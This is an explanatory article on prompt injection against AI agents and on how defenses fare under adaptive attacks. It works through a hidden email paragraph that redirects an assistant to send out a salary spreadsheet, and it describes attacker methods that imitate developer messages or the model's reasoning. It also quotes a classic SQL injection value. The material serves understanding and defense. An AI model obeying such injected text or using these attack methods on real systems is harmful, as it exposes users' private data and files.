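# Prompt-injection defenses, least agency and sandboxing for AI agents

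## How AI agents use tools and how injected text takes them over

An AI agent is a language model that a program runs in a loop. The model chooses an action, the program carries it out, and the model reads the result and chooses the next action, until the task is complete. Each action is a tool call, a structured request to run a function such as searching a mailbox, editing a file or paying an invoice. Agents increasingly work in critical infrastructure and defense, according to *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), guidance that the Australian Signals Directorate wrote with its counterparts in the United States, Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom. The guidance advises organizations to give agents only low-risk, non-sensitive tasks.

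One reason for the caution is prompt injection, text that makes a model act for an attacker. An agent reads a lot of text that its user did not write, and anyone who can add to that text can try to redirect the agent.

### The agent loop

An AI office assistant might have four tools, which let it read email, read files, send email and run code. Its developer has written a system prompt, a set of standing instructions that describes the job and lists the tools. A user asks the assistant to summarize the overnight email and flag whatever needs an answer today.

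The program joins the system prompt and the request into one text, called the context, and passes it to the model. *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2026) includes two optional steps at this point. Some agents fetch documents from a database and add them to the context, and some have the model write out its reasoning before it acts. The model then produces a tool call, a short text containing a function's name and the values to run it with. Here the function is the email reader, and the value is a start time of 6 p.m. the day before.

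The model cannot open the mailbox, so the surrounding program reads the call, runs the function with the assistant's permissions, and appends the output to the context. Here the output is the full text of nine messages. The program then sends the whole context back to the model, which produces either another call or a final answer. A sequence of calls in which one call's output shapes the next is a tool chain.

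A plain chatbot is easier to guard than an agent. Chu (2026) points out in *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* that a model without memory or tools takes one input and gives one output, so a filter on each side covers it. An agent also carries state from one step to the next and takes actions along the way.

### One email that redirects the assistant

Suppose that one of the nine messages comes from a stranger who poses as a supplier. It asks about an invoice. Below the signature, in white letters on a white background, sits a further paragraph addressed to the assistant. It claims that the user wants the salary spreadsheet to go to an outside accountant, gives an address, and adds that the summary need not mention this. If the injection works, the run goes as follows:

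1. The assistant calls the email reader, as the user wanted, and the hidden paragraph enters the context along with everything else.
2. The model's next call opens the salary spreadsheet.
3. The contents of the spreadsheet enter the context, and the model calls the email sender with those contents and the stranger's address.
4. The model writes a tidy summary of nine messages, one of them an invoice query.

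The attacker needed no password and exploited no bug in the mail software. The assistant had permission to make each of these calls, so checks that look at one call at a time can miss an attack like this. With the code tool, the attacker could have used a different paragraph to request a script that deletes the user's files.

An injection is never certain to work, because models do not give the same output every time and many ignore crude attempts. But the attacker can easily send another email with different wording.

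### Instructions and data in one sequence

A language model processes text as tokens, which are fragments represented as numbers, and predicts the next token from those before it. It receives the system prompt, the user's request, the nine emails and its own earlier output as one sequence, "glued together", as Willison (2025) puts it in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*.

Developers put tags around each stretch of text to show whether it comes from the developer, the user or a tool, and they train models to give the tags weight. But the tags are only more tokens in the sequence, and the model has to learn what they imply. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, trained classifiers on the internal activity of several models to find out which source a model attributes a passage to. Style affected the attribution more than the tag did, and models attributed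 a passage that sounded like a user's command to the user even when it was inside a tag for tool output. This fits the hidden paragraph in the example, whose author would naturally write it to sound like the user. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) describes such tags as useful engineering but not a hard security boundary.

*ASIDE* (Zverev, Kortukov and colleagues, 2025) builds the boundary between commands and data into the model. In a standard model, each token has one embedding, the list of numbers that represents it at the first layer, whether it occurs in a command or in a document. ASIDE takes the numbers of every data token in pairs and rotates each pair by 90 degrees, so that the two kinds of token are represented differently from the start. Across several models of 7 to 13 billion parameters, this cut the average success rate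 of attacks from 14.7% to 4.9% on one test set and from 45.6% to 28.1% on a harder one, without any training against attacks. The tests were single exchanges, with no loop in which an attacker gets several chances.

### The comparison with SQL injection

The name "prompt injection" comes from SQL injection, an older attack on databases. Many websites use databases that take commands in a language called SQL, and a careless programmer builds a command by pasting a visitor's input into it. *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3* (Willison, 2022) gives the classic example of a command that looks up a username. If a visitor enters `'; drop table users;` as the name, the quotation mark ends the name early, and the database runs the text after it as a second command, which deletes the table of users.

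Parameterized queries fix this. The programmer writes the command with a placeholder, as in `select * from users where username = ?`, and supplies the visitor's input separately. The database then treats the input as a value to look up and never as a command, whatever characters it contains.

In 2022, Willison hoped for a language model with one slot for instructions and others for data. A reader pointed him to an OpenAI model that already had separate slots, but injections in the data slot still worked on it. By April 2023 he had added a note that the fix looked extremely difficult, if not impossible, on the architectures of the time.

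The UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) published the fullest version of this argument in December 2025, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*. The NCSC's technical director for platforms research, who publishes as David C, wrote that a database engine processes instructions and data differently, and parameterized queries enforce that difference. A language model has no such difference to enforce, because "there is only ever 'next token'". Filters that look for injections, training that ranks instructions above data, and markers around untrusted text all try to add the distinction to a technology that lacks it. He worries that security staff who know SQL injection will expect a similar fix for prompt injection and build systems as though one existed.

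David C proposes a different comparison, the confused deputy, which is a program tricked into using its privileges on behalf of someone who lacks them. In the classic example, a compiler had permission to write to a billing file that ordinary users could not touch. A user told the compiler to write its output to that file, and it overwrote the bills. Designers can fix such a program, for instance by making the caller supply the permission along with the request. David C calls language models "inherently confusable" because no equivalent fix exists for them. He concludes that designers should assume an injection can do whatever an attacker with direct access to the tools could do. For the office assistant, that means reading the files, sending mail in the user's name and running code. If an organization cannot accept the risk that remains after safeguards, the task may be a poor fit for a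 language model.

David C's argument is a forecast that there is "a good chance" no proper fix will come. ASIDE shows that model architectures can change, though so far the change has only reduced the problem. The argument also does not apply to controls outside the model. A mail server that refuses to deliver to unknown addresses does so whatever the model has read, and David C wants designers to concentrate on deterministic safeguards like this.

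### Direct injection, indirect injection and jailbreaking

*Exploring Prompt Injection Attacks* (Selvi, 2022) recounts that Jon Cefalu reported the flaw privately to OpenAI in May 2022 and that Riley Goodside published examples that September. Willison named the flaw "prompt injection" a day after Goodside's post. Goodside's examples were direct injections, in which the attacker types to the model himself. Goodside asked a model to translate a sentence that told it to ignore the request and output something else.

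In an indirect injection, the attacker doesn't interact with the system directly but leaves text where the model will later read it while working for a user, who becomes the victim. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) introduced the idea and demonstrated it against Microsoft's Bing Chat, among other systems. An attacker can plant the text on a web page and push the page up the search rankings, send it by email, or hide it in a snippet that people copy and paste. A short injection can also direct the model to fetch a longer one from elsewhere. The paper closely anticipated the office assistant's problem, including a version in which the hijacked assistant emails the injection to the user's contacts and so spreads it like a worm. The email in the running example is an indirect injection, as is David C's example of a job applicant's CV with a hidden instruction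 for the screening software to approve it.

Jailbreaking means getting a model to break its maker's rules on content, for example to give a recipe for a weapon. The attacker is the user, and the usual harm is a text that the model should have refused to write. Willison insists on distinguishing jailbreaking from prompt injection, because developers who confuse them conclude that injection only embarrasses the model maker and doesn't concern them. But Pillar Security's *The terminology problem causing security teams real risks* notes that two widely used threat catalogues, from OWASP and MITRE, class jailbreaking as a form of prompt injection. Some vendors also promise "prompt injection protection" without saying which attacks they mean, so a buyer of an email agent should ask about indirect injection.

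### The lethal trifecta

An agent can be made to leak secrets when it has access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. Willison named this combination the lethal trifecta. Untrusted content is anything the agent reads that someone other than its user or developer could have written. The office assistant has all three parts of the trifecta, and its mailbox alone contains both private data and untrusted content.

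Removing any one of the three prevents this kind of theft, at least in principle. In practice, the outward route is hard to close because data can leave through actions that don't look like sending. The web address of an image that a tool loads, or of a link that the user clicks, can contain stolen data. The trifecta also covers only theft. An assistant that can't send anything out can still delete files or corrupt a spreadsheet when an email contains injected instructions to do so.

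### Measuring attacks and defenses

Researchers mainly report two numbers, attack success rate and utility. Attack success rate is the share of attack attempts, or of attacked scenarios, in which the agent does what the attacker wanted. Utility is the share of legitimate tasks that the agent still completes with a defense in place. Neither means much alone, since an assistant that refuses every request has an attack success rate of zero but completes no legitimate tasks.

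Many of the published figures come from the benchmark *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024). It simulates four settings (an office workspace, the chat service Slack, a travel agency and a bank) with 74 tools among them. It includes 97 user tasks, such as paying a bill, and 27 attacker goals, such as sending a security code to an outside address. Pairing every task with every goal in the same setting gives 629 security cases. In each case, the injected text is somewhere a stranger could have put it, such as the body of an email.

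After each run, code checks the simulated world to see whether the agent transferred the money or sent the message. The designers did not use a second language model as the judge, because an injection that takes over the agent could also take over the judge. They measure benign utility (tasks solved without an attack), utility under attack (user tasks solved during an attack without harmful side effects) and the targeted attack success rate.

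The first results are for models from 2024, all of which solved fewer than 66% of the tasks even without an attack. A generic injection, which presented the attacker's goal as an important message to deal with first, succeeded against OpenAI's GPT-4o in 47.7% of cases when it addressed the user and the model by their correct names. Getting either name wrong cut the rate to about 23%. In the Slack setting, where attackers control much of what the agent reads, the rate was 92%. More capable models tended to be easier to attack, perhaps because weaker models failed at the attacker's task as well as the user's. Attack success and utility both matter when judging a defense. For example, a detector that stopped the run at any suspected injection cut attack success to 8%, but it raised so many false alarms that utility fell significantly.

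AgentDojo is still in heavy use. *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (2026) ran 13 models from six providers on it, and *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) describes a version with more than 900 pairings. Many of its results, however, come from static attacks, which use a fixed set of texts, whereas a real attacker can adapt the text to the defense. Debenedetti and colleagues themselves warned that it is extremely easy to build a defense against one particular attack that stops little else. Wang and colleagues object that in most existing benchmark tasks, the user's request contains all the instructions the agent needs. Real users also say things like "do what the checklist in this file asks". A defense that makes the agent ignore all instructions in what it reads will score well on such benchmarks but fail those users.

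### What counts as prevention

Prevention covers controls that act before a tool call or when it is made. Detection, response and recovery come afterwards. Most advice on securing agents draws on three types of prevention.

One family of defenses tries to stop injected text from steering the model, either through training and filtering or by designing the agent so that untrusted text cannot affect which tools it calls. A second family limits what the agent may do. Least privilege means giving a program only the permissions its task requires, which would keep the office assistant out of the salary folder. Least agency extends this rule to how much the agent may do unsupervised. The third family puts the agent in a sandbox, an environment enforced outside the model that restricts which files, processes and network addresses the agent can reach. A script that the assistant runs there could not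 contact the attacker's server, regardless of why the model wrote it.

Official advice mixes the families. *NCSC Urges Stronger Controls for Agentic AI Systems* (Mascellino, 2026) reports that in August 2026 the NCSC urged sandboxing, human oversight and tight access controls together. Sandboxing counts as prevention by its timing, because a sandbox blocks a forbidden connection when the agent attempts it, before any data leaves. Some authors class it as containment instead because it does nothing to keep the model from being fooled and only limits the damage afterwards, which is a fair description of its purpose.

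## Defenses that train, instruct or filter the model

The most direct way to protect the office assistant would be to have its model read the stranger's email without obeying it. Developers have tried formatting the prompt so that untrusted text stands out, training the model to ignore commands in such text, screening the text with a separate detector, and running a check that relies on something the attacker doesn't know. None of these defenses changes the assistant's tools or permissions, so an email that gets past them can still make the assistant send out the salary spreadsheet.

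Most developers of such defenses reported attack success rates close to zero. In October 2025, fourteen researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and other institutions retested twelve published defenses, ten against prompt injection and two against jailbreaks, using attacks adapted to each one. The attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defenses (Nasr, Carlini et al., *The Attacker Moves Second*, 2025).

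### How an adaptive attack works

Nasr and colleagues describe an adaptive attack as a four-step loop. The attacker proposes candidate texts, scores each by how the defended system responds to it, selects the promising ones, and updates the method or the pool of candidates before the next round. For example, if the assistant ignores a hidden paragraph that gives a blunt order, the next version might present the same request as office procedure.

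They ran this loop in four ways:

- **Gradient attacks** use the model's internal weights to calculate which change of token would most raise the probability of the output the attacker wants. The team found these unreliable on language models and used them against only one defense.
- **Reinforcement-learning attacks** train a second language model as the attacker. It gets five tries per session, sees the response and a score after each, and goes through 32 sessions per case. Training then adjusts its weights toward whatever scored well.
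- **Search attacks** keep a pool of candidate injections and have a language model, Gemini 2.5 Pro, rewrite the better ones. A further model grades each attempt from 1 to 10, because a bare yes or no would give the search no way to recognize progress. Each search could query the target up to 800 times.
- **Human attackers** took part in an online contest with over 500 participants and $20,000 in prizes. They typed injections into a web page and watched the agent's reasoning and tool calls as it responded.

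For each defense, the team picked the attacks that seemed most likely to work, without trying to limit the resources they required. Security researchers conventionally assume that an attacker knows how a defense works and has plenty of computing power, because a defense that stops only uninformed attackers offers little protection. Defense papers had largely dropped that convention. Of the 37 attack papers that Wang and colleagues surveyed, 14 already used automated optimization, while defenses and benchmarks still relied mainly on hand-written templates.

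### Prompting

Spotlighting changes how untrusted text looks before it reaches the model and adds an explanation of the change to the system prompt. Hines, Lopez and colleagues (2024) describe three versions in *Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks With Spotlighting*. Delimiting puts a symbol before and after the document and tells the model never to obey anything between them. Datamarking replaces every space in the document with a special character, so the whole text is marked. Encoding converts the document into a scheme such as base64, which a capable model can decode as it works.

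Hines and colleagues at Microsoft tested all three on 1,000 documents containing variations of one simple attack, a command to forget earlier instructions and answer with a single keyword. When GPT-3.5 Turbo summarized the documents without a defense, the attack worked at least half the time. Delimiters roughly halved the success rate, datamarking cut it to about 3%, and encoding cut it to zero. Datamarking did not hurt performance on four standard language tests. Encoding badly hurt the performance of GPT-3.5 Turbo, which made decoding mistakes, but had little effect on GPT-4. The team recommended datamarking as a minimum and encoding for the strongest models. They advised against delimiters because an attacker who learns the system prompt can insert the same symbols.

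Google's experience suggests that these results may come largely from garbling particular attack phrases. Its engineers inserted a marker after every eight characters of an email's sender, subject and body. According to *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025), this worked mainly by breaking the attack's trigger phrases into unusual tokens. If so, an attacker could look for other phrases that still work with the markers inserted.

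Prompt sandwiching repeats the user's request after the untrusted text, which it leaves unchanged. The office assistant would read the request, then the nine emails, then the request again, so that the user's request is the last thing it reads.

On the AgentDojo benchmark, Nasr and colleagues found that static attacks succeeded as little as 1% of the time against Spotlighting and sandwiching. Their search attack succeeded more than 95% of the time against both. Contestants contributed 265 successful attacks on Spotlighting and 178 on sandwiching. A common trick was to present the attacker's task as a step the assistant had to complete before it could do what the user wanted. Sandwiching, which repeats the user's request, does little against this trick because the attacker's task appears necessary to fulfill that request.

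The low starting figure of 1% was for Spotlighting on a model whose developers had already trained it against injection. On Gemini 2.5 Pro, static attacks succeeded 28% of the time with Spotlighting and 30% with no defense. But the version the team describes uses delimiters, which Spotlighting's inventors advised against, so the result is weaker evidence about the encoding version.

### Training

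*StruQ* (2024) separates the developer's instruction from outside data by having a program put each into its own labeled field before they reach the model. The model's training includes examples with a simulated injection in the data field, for which the correct answer responds only to the instruction field. The paper reports security against a wide range of human-written injections, including some adapted to the defense, and partial improvement against optimized attacks.

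*Meta-SecAlign* (2025) uses the same separation but trains on pairs of answers. Each pair starts with an ordinary example, such as a request to summarize an article, and an instruction from another example is hidden in the article. Before this training, the model writes one answer to the original request with a clean article and another to the hidden instruction. Direct preference optimization (DPO) then trains the model to make the first answer more probable and the second less probable when it reads the article with the injection. Since both answers are in the model's own style, training is less likely to change anything besides the choice between them. The trained model runs as fast as before.

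Meta-SecAlign's developers reported a 2% attack success rate on AgentDojo, but Nasr and colleagues reached 96% with the search attack. They evaluated StruQ with its paper's own test, in which the attacker tries to make the model print a fixed phrase. Their reinforcement-learning attacker succeeded in every case, mostly with texts that imitated a message from the developer. Circuit Breakers, a training defense against jailbreaks, also failed every time.

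Nasr's team had seen the same problem in image recognition, where networks trained on a fixed set of doctored images kept failing against new ones. Lasting improvement came only when researchers generated new attacks against the network throughout its training. StruQ and Meta-SecAlign both trained on attacks that did not adapt to the model.

Commercial developers have taken up a broader version of the training approach. *The Instruction Hierarchy* (Wallace, Xiao and colleagues, 2024), a paper from OpenAI, ranks sources of text by privilege, with the developer's system message at the top, then the user, and tool outputs at the bottom. The model should follow a lower-ranking instruction that agrees with those above it, such as a user's request that a car-sales chatbot speak Spanish. It should ignore an instruction that conflicts with those above it, or refuse when there is no way to proceed.

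The team generated training data for both situations. For instructions that agree, it split a request such as "write a 20 line poem in spanish" into parts, placed them at different levels, and trained the model to answer as if it had received the whole request at once. For conflicting instructions, it trained the model to answer as if it had never seen them. This first version treated every instruction on a web page or in a tool's output as conflicting. This rule is simple to teach, but it does not suit an assistant whose user has asked it to follow the checklist in a file.

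With this training, GPT-3.5 Turbo became 63% better at keeping its system message secret and over 30% more robust to jailbreaks, which the training data had not included. It also ignored or refused some harmless requests. The hierarchy depends on the surrounding program labeling each passage correctly. *When Context Gets Root* (2026) points out that training makes a model give more weight to any text with a privileged label, so an attacker who can forge the label benefits from the training. A 2025 attack called RL-Hammer, which trained an attacker by reinforcement learning, got injections past both GPT-5 and Gemini 2.5 despite their built-in hierarchies, according to Kurakin, Karande and colleagues in *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (2026).

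### Separate detectors

A detector is a second, usually much smaller model that inspects text entering or leaving the main one. It scores how likely each passage is to be an attack, and the program removes or blocks passages that score above a threshold. For the office assistant, a detector would check each email before it reached the main model. Detectors are popular because they can be added to any model without retraining it.

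Nasr and colleagues tested four detectors. Protect AI's detector, Meta's PromptGuard and the academic PIGuard are versions of BERT, an older and smaller kind of language model, that their developers trained on a mixture of harmless prompts and known attacks. The fourth, Google's Model Armor, is proprietary. The attacker could see each detector's verdict and confidence score during the search. When the detectors were placed one at a time in front of Gemini 2.5 Pro, the search attack succeeded in at least 90% of cases against Protect AI, PromptGuard and Model Armor, and in 71% against PIGuard. The contest produced hundreds of successful attacks on detectors, including 123 under the strictest conditions.

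Many of the successful injections looked like routine office messages. They did not tell the model to ignore anything, and a reader who saw them out of context would have struggled to say what was wrong with them. A detector strict enough to catch them would also block a lot of genuine email. Combining several detectors did not stop the attacks either.

The team concedes that detectors are easy to install and block some unsophisticated or opportunistic attacks, which makes them a useful but limited part of a larger defense. That seems fair, because many real attackers will copy a known injection from the internet, and a detector trained on known injections is likely to catch it.

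### Checks that rely on a secret

DataSentinel tests each piece of untrusted text on a separate detector model before the main model uses it. It gives the detector a secret key, asks it to repeat the key once, and tells it to ignore the text that follows. If the detector fails to repeat the key, something in the text has presumably diverted it, and DataSentinel rejects the text. Otherwise the text passes. DataSentinel's developers trained the detector to be especially easy to divert, and reported that it caught almost all attacks, including some that they had adapted to the defense.

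Nasr's team used two classification tasks from DataSentinel's tests, sentiment analysis and spam detection. The attacker had to turn one task into the other without setting off the check. Its first attempts all failed, but partway through training it found a few texts that partly worked and quickly improved them. The finished attacks bypassed the check in every case, and the diverted model did the attacker's task with over 80% accuracy, about as well as with no defense. The attacks redefined the terms of the task, which keeps the form of the answer the same and leaves little for a checker to detect.

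MELON compares two runs of the agent. In the first, the agent works on the user's request and MELON records its tool calls. In the second, MELON replaces the request with a harmless one to summarize what the tools returned. If the agent tries to send someone a spreadsheet in both runs, the instruction probably came from the emails it read, because summarizing the overnight email should not involve sending a spreadsheet. The second run requires extra compute.

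The search attack reached a 76% success rate against MELON on Llama 3.3 70B without any knowledge of the defense, by chancing on injections that triggered the harmful call only during the real task. When the attacker had MELON's paper and code, the rate rose to 95%. The search then quickly found conditional injections, which ask for one action if the task is the user's and something innocuous if the task is a summary. The wording of MELON's second request, the summary task, was secret, but an attacker needed only to guess what kind of task it was.

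### Seven defenses on one model

Nasr and colleagues warn against ranking the twelve defenses by their headline figures, because they followed each defense's original test and those tests differ. But they also published results for seven of the defenses using the same underlying model, Gemini 2.5 Pro, and the same 80 AgentDojo cases. The utility figures cover all of AgentDojo's user tasks.

| Defense | Static attack success | Search attack success | Utility |
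|---|---|---|---|
| None | 30% | 100% | 74% |
| Spotlighting | 28% | 99% | 75% |
| Prompt sandwiching | 21% | 95% | 73% |
| PromptGuard | 26% | 94% | 72% |
| Model Armor | 28% | 90% | 59% |
| Protect AI | 15% | 90% | 39% |
| MELON | 0% | 89% | 58% |
| PIGuard | 0% | 71% | 39% |

Four of the seven defenses barely affected even the static attack. The two that stopped it completely, MELON and PIGuard, reduced utility considerably, PIGuard by nearly half. PIGuard's relatively good 71% therefore comes from a detector that also blocks much of what the user wants done, and the researchers doubt that it would keep its advantage at a tolerable false-alarm rate. Protect AI's figures exclude some attacks that could not work because the detector had wrongly flagged the secret itself as an injection and removed it.

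Wang and colleagues found a similar trade-off when they tested eight defenses on tasks that require the agent to act on what it reads. No defense combined trustworthiness, high utility and low delay. Text filters were quick but did not hold up against sophisticated injections, while some controls on the agent's actions needed up to three times the normal computation.

The choice of underlying model also matters. With no defense, the search attack succeeded against GPT-5 Mini 75% of the time. Spotlighting reduced that to 47%, the best result for any defense on any of the models. No static attack succeeded against GPT-5 Mini, with or without a defense, so a developer who ran only static attacks would have called the model safe.

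### People compared with automated search

The contest and the search attack overlapped in 29 scenarios, each a combination of a task, a model and a defense. In each scenario, at least one person succeeded, while the search attack succeeded in 69% of them after 800 queries. As a group, people also needed fewer queries.

That comparison favors the humans because it sets hundreds of independent people against a single run of a search program whose results vary a lot between runs. Of the three people who attempted all 29 scenarios, the best succeeded in 75%, slightly more than the search, and the other two did worse than the search.

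Individual submissions usually failed. With MELON, 0.4% of submissions succeeded against Gemini 2.5 Pro in its reasoning mode, down from 11.1% without it. With the Protect AI detector, the success rate on several models was higher than without it, probably more because of who was submitting and how much practice they had than because of the detector. The per-attempt success rate matters to an attacker who can send one email to one company, but an attacker who can send thousands cares more about whether any attempt succeeds.

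### How much help the attackers had

Nasr's attackers had advantages that a stranger writing to the office assistant would lack. They could query the defended system hundreds of times and fit each injection to a known user task, and in some tests they could see the detector's confidence score. The study tested whether defenses could be broken but did not measure how hard it would be to break them. It left out designs that plan the agent's actions before reading any untrusted text, because an attack on such a design is bound to fail in most of its test scenarios.

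The attacker's computing budget may matter less than it first appears. On Gemini 2.5 Pro, the median successful search needed 14 queries against Spotlighting and 46 against PIGuard, and anyone who can set up their own copy of a commercial assistant can run that many. Knowing the user's task and seeing the detector's score are bigger advantages than a large computing budget.

In *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026), the attacker doesn't know which defense is running or what the user has asked for. It writes one injection that has to work across several user requests, and learns only how often it succeeded. A language model uses the scores so far to guess what kind of defense is running, then writes a new version. The process takes six rounds.

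Even so, the attack success rate against PIGuard on GPT-4o mini rose from zero with the static attack to 28.0%. The rate rose from 7.2% to 15.4% against Protect AI, and from 12.6% to 33.4% against DataFilter, which uses a language model to strip out injections. On Gemini 2.5 Flash, the rate against PIGuard reached only 4.6%. These rates are much lower than Nasr's and probably a better guide to what a moderately equipped outsider could do, though the two studies used different models. The loss of utility was much the same, with PIGuard and Protect AI preventing the agent from completing between a quarter and a half of its ordinary tasks.

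Injections succeeded much more often when the user stated the task less precisely. With PIGuard on GPT-4o mini, they succeeded 17.3% of the time when the user specified the action and all its details, such as a change to a given address. The rate was 54.2% when the user left the action itself to outside content, for example by asking the agent to do everything on a to-do list. An injection on a to-do list can be just another item, so a detector that looks for text resembling a command will miss it.

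Ma and colleagues also tested four defenses that restrict the agent's actions, and these mostly held up better. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) cautions against trusting such defenses too soon. It argues that prompt injection in an agent with tools is a problem of authorization, and that the first generation of defenses wrongly treated it as a problem of content. But according to the paper, researchers have mostly evaluated the second generation the same way as the first, on fixed sets of attacks.

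### Training that held up better in 2026

In two projects from 2026, training defenses did better on adaptive tests than earlier ones had. *SecOPD* (Peng, Lian and colleagues, 2026) starts from a weakness in how Meta-SecAlign is trained. A model that reads an injection often answers the user properly and then carries out the injected instruction in its last sentence. Meta-SecAlign's training compares whole answers, so it gives the model no signal about which part was wrong.

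SecOPD grades every token. The model in training, called the student, reads a document with an injection and writes an answer. A frozen copy of the original model, the teacher, reads the same document without the injection and calculates how likely it would have been to write each of the student's tokens. The score for token number *t* is

score(*t*) = log P_teacher(token *t* | clean input, earlier tokens) − log P_student(token *t* | attacked input, earlier tokens)

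A token that answers the user is about as likely under the teacher as under the student, so its score is near zero or positive. A token that obeys the injection is very unlikely under the teacher, whose input doesn't contain the injection, so its score is strongly negative and training makes it less likely. The researchers can use such a teacher in training because they inserted the injections themselves. It couldn't exist in real use, where nobody knows which part of an email is the attack.

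The team applied several training methods to the same model, Qwen3.6-27B, and attacked the resulting models in three ways. The static test combined six hand-written attacks. A simple adaptive attack imitated the markers that separate messages in this model's input. The strongest attack, PISmith, trained a new attacker model against each defense and had ten tries at each of 1,024 cases. GRPO in the table is a reinforcement-learning method that gives each whole answer one score.

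| Training | Static | Simple adaptive | PISmith |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 99.4% | 99.0% | 97.9% |
| Meta-SecAlign | 28.9% | 5.5% | 94.0% |
| GRPO | 15.0% | 2.3% | 61.2% |
| SecOPD | 1.3% | 0.2% | 9.0% |

Average utility over seven benchmarks was 88.1%, the same as for the untrained model. The middle column shows that a result labeled "adaptive" can be misleading. A developer who tried only the simple adaptive attack on Meta-SecAlign would have reported 5.5%, which is lower than the static figure and far below 94%.

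Peng and colleagues see their result as a challenge to the view that one can never rely on the model for security. It is the best result against adaptive attacks for a training defense that anyone can download and test, but the PISmith cases involved only text answers. On AgentDojo, where the agent uses tools, the team ran only a static attack, and SecOPD's 4.7% was hardly better than Meta-SecAlign's 5.5%. The training also teaches the model to reason as though the injection weren't there, so a monitor that reads its reasoning for signs of an attack may find none. The team expects that stronger attackers may break the defense.

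OpenAI went further by training an attacker and a group of defenders together (Wallace, Choquette-Choo and colleagues, 2026, *GPT-Red*). In each round, the attacker may edit one thing that an outsider could plausibly control, such as an email body or a search result, and can test drafts on the defender before submitting one. The attacker earns a reward if the defender carries out the attack, and the defender earns one for resisting and finishing the user's task. With a single defender, the attacker tended to settle on one kind of trick, so the team used many defenders. Early in training, the attacker wrote crude orders to ignore previous instructions. Later it learned to write text that looked like the defender's own reasoning, which the defender then continued as its own.

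This is the kind of training that Nasr's team had said was missing, and it used roughly as much computing power as the reinforcement-learning stage of OpenAI's recent commercial models. On scenarios from a 2025 public contest, GPT-Red found more working injections than the human contestants had, reversing the October 2025 result. OpenAI then used GPT-Red's attacks to train GPT-5.6. In a test on scenarios outside the training set, fewer than 4% of attacks on GPT-5.6 succeeded. That result may overstate the model's robustness, because GPT-Red was again the attacker. However, the test also switched off the safeguards that surround the model in OpenAI's products, which would otherwise have given it more protection. The team calls robustness "far from solved".

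A score of this kind also depends on how strong the attacker is. At Google DeepMind, Kurakin and colleagues had sixteen AI agents work together on each injection, sharing notes and a leaderboard of the best attempts. The goal was always a harmless tool call unrelated to the user's request, such as logging someone's blood pressure during a tutoring task, so that a model could not pass just by recognizing a dangerous action. When three weaker Gemini models played the attackers, Gemini 4 Argon resisted in every scenario. When Argon also played the attackers, it resisted in 87% of scenarios over 150 attempts and in 66% over the full budget of 320. Argon was better than the weaker attackers at making the unwanted call look like something the user's task required.

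The researchers conclude that developers should not rely only on hardening the model. They also found that outsiders can do little to check claims of robustness, because most teams keep their attack programs private for fear of misuse. The only public program they could run succeeded in 2 of 80 AgentDojo scenarios against an older Gemini model with its usual safeguards on. A version of their own attack succeeded in 6 of the 80, using at most 25 queries per scenario.

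## How often injection succeeds against current models

Published attack success rates for the newest models range from zero to more than half of all attempts, and Claude Fable 5.1 has had results at both ends of that range. The rate depends on the agent's task, how many tries the attacker had, how well the attacks suited the model, and which safeguards were in place around it. A percentage reported without those details is a poor measure of an agent's safety.

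### Fable 5.1 in three settings

Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Fable 5.1, a collection of test results dated September 1, gives separate figures for three kinds of agent. Coding agents read and edit software projects, computer-use agents operate a graphical desktop, and browser agents read web pages and act on them.

In the coding and computer-use tests, the attacker was Shade, an automated tool from the security company Gray Swan that combines search, reinforcement learning and insights from human testers. It had 200 attempts at each scenario. For the coding test, Gray Swan trained Shade on the same 40 scenarios against earlier Claude models, then ran it unchanged against Fable 5.1. The company also built a stronger version, trained longer on a wider variety of attacks. For the browser test, Anthropic reused attacks that professional testers had developed against the older Claude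 Opus 4.7, and allowed ten attempts per scenario.

Anthropic ran each test with and without its safeguards against injection. The coding and computer use tests used detectors called probes, which screen tool results before the model acts on them. The browser test used auto mode, which adds a classifier that blocks potentially dangerous tool calls. Each cell in the table gives the share of attempts that succeeded, then the number of scenarios in which at least one attempt succeeded.

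| Setting | Attempts per scenario | Without injection safeguards | With them |
|---|---|---|---|
| Coding, original Shade | 200 | 9.26%; 31 of 40 | 2.05%; 18 of 40 |
| Coding, stronger Shade | 200 | 56.87%; 38 of 40 | 12.80%; 36 of 40 |
| Computer use, Shade | 200 | 0.07%; 2 of 14 | 0.07%; 2 of 14 |
| Browser, reused attacks | 10 | 2.64%; 10 of 110 | 0%; 0 of 110 |

Against the stronger coding attacker, the probes cut successful attempts by more than three quarters, but the number of scenarios in which the attacker succeeded at least once fell only from 38 to 36. Probes like these would hardly help against someone who can try 200 times, though they would help a lot against someone who gets a single try.

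Anthropic calls the Shade tests deliberately permissive toward attackers, because real attackers usually don't know the target's setup and repeated attempts make detection more likely. That seems right, but the coding and browser tests were easier on the model in one respect, because their attacks were developed by practicing on earlier models, while anyone with an account can practice on the current one.

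The zero in the browser row does not rule out successful attacks. If something never happens in *n* independent trials, its true rate could still be as high as about 3/*n*, at 95% confidence. Ten attempts at one scenario are not independent, so it is safer to set *n* to 110, the number of scenarios. Attacks could therefore still work in up to 2.7% of similar scenarios. Opus 5 had also scored zero in July, over 129 scenarios, which led The Decoder to title an article *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. The same article cites OpenAI's admission in December that injection may never be fully solved.

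Still, auto mode works against this set of attacks. In Anthropic's July tests, browser attacks on another of its models, Claude Mythos 5, succeeded in 29.7% of attempts without safeguards and in none with auto mode on. The original Shade had succeeded in only 0.45% of coding attempts against that model, so a low rate in one setting does not reliably predict a low rate in another.

### A safeguard that brought in a weaker model

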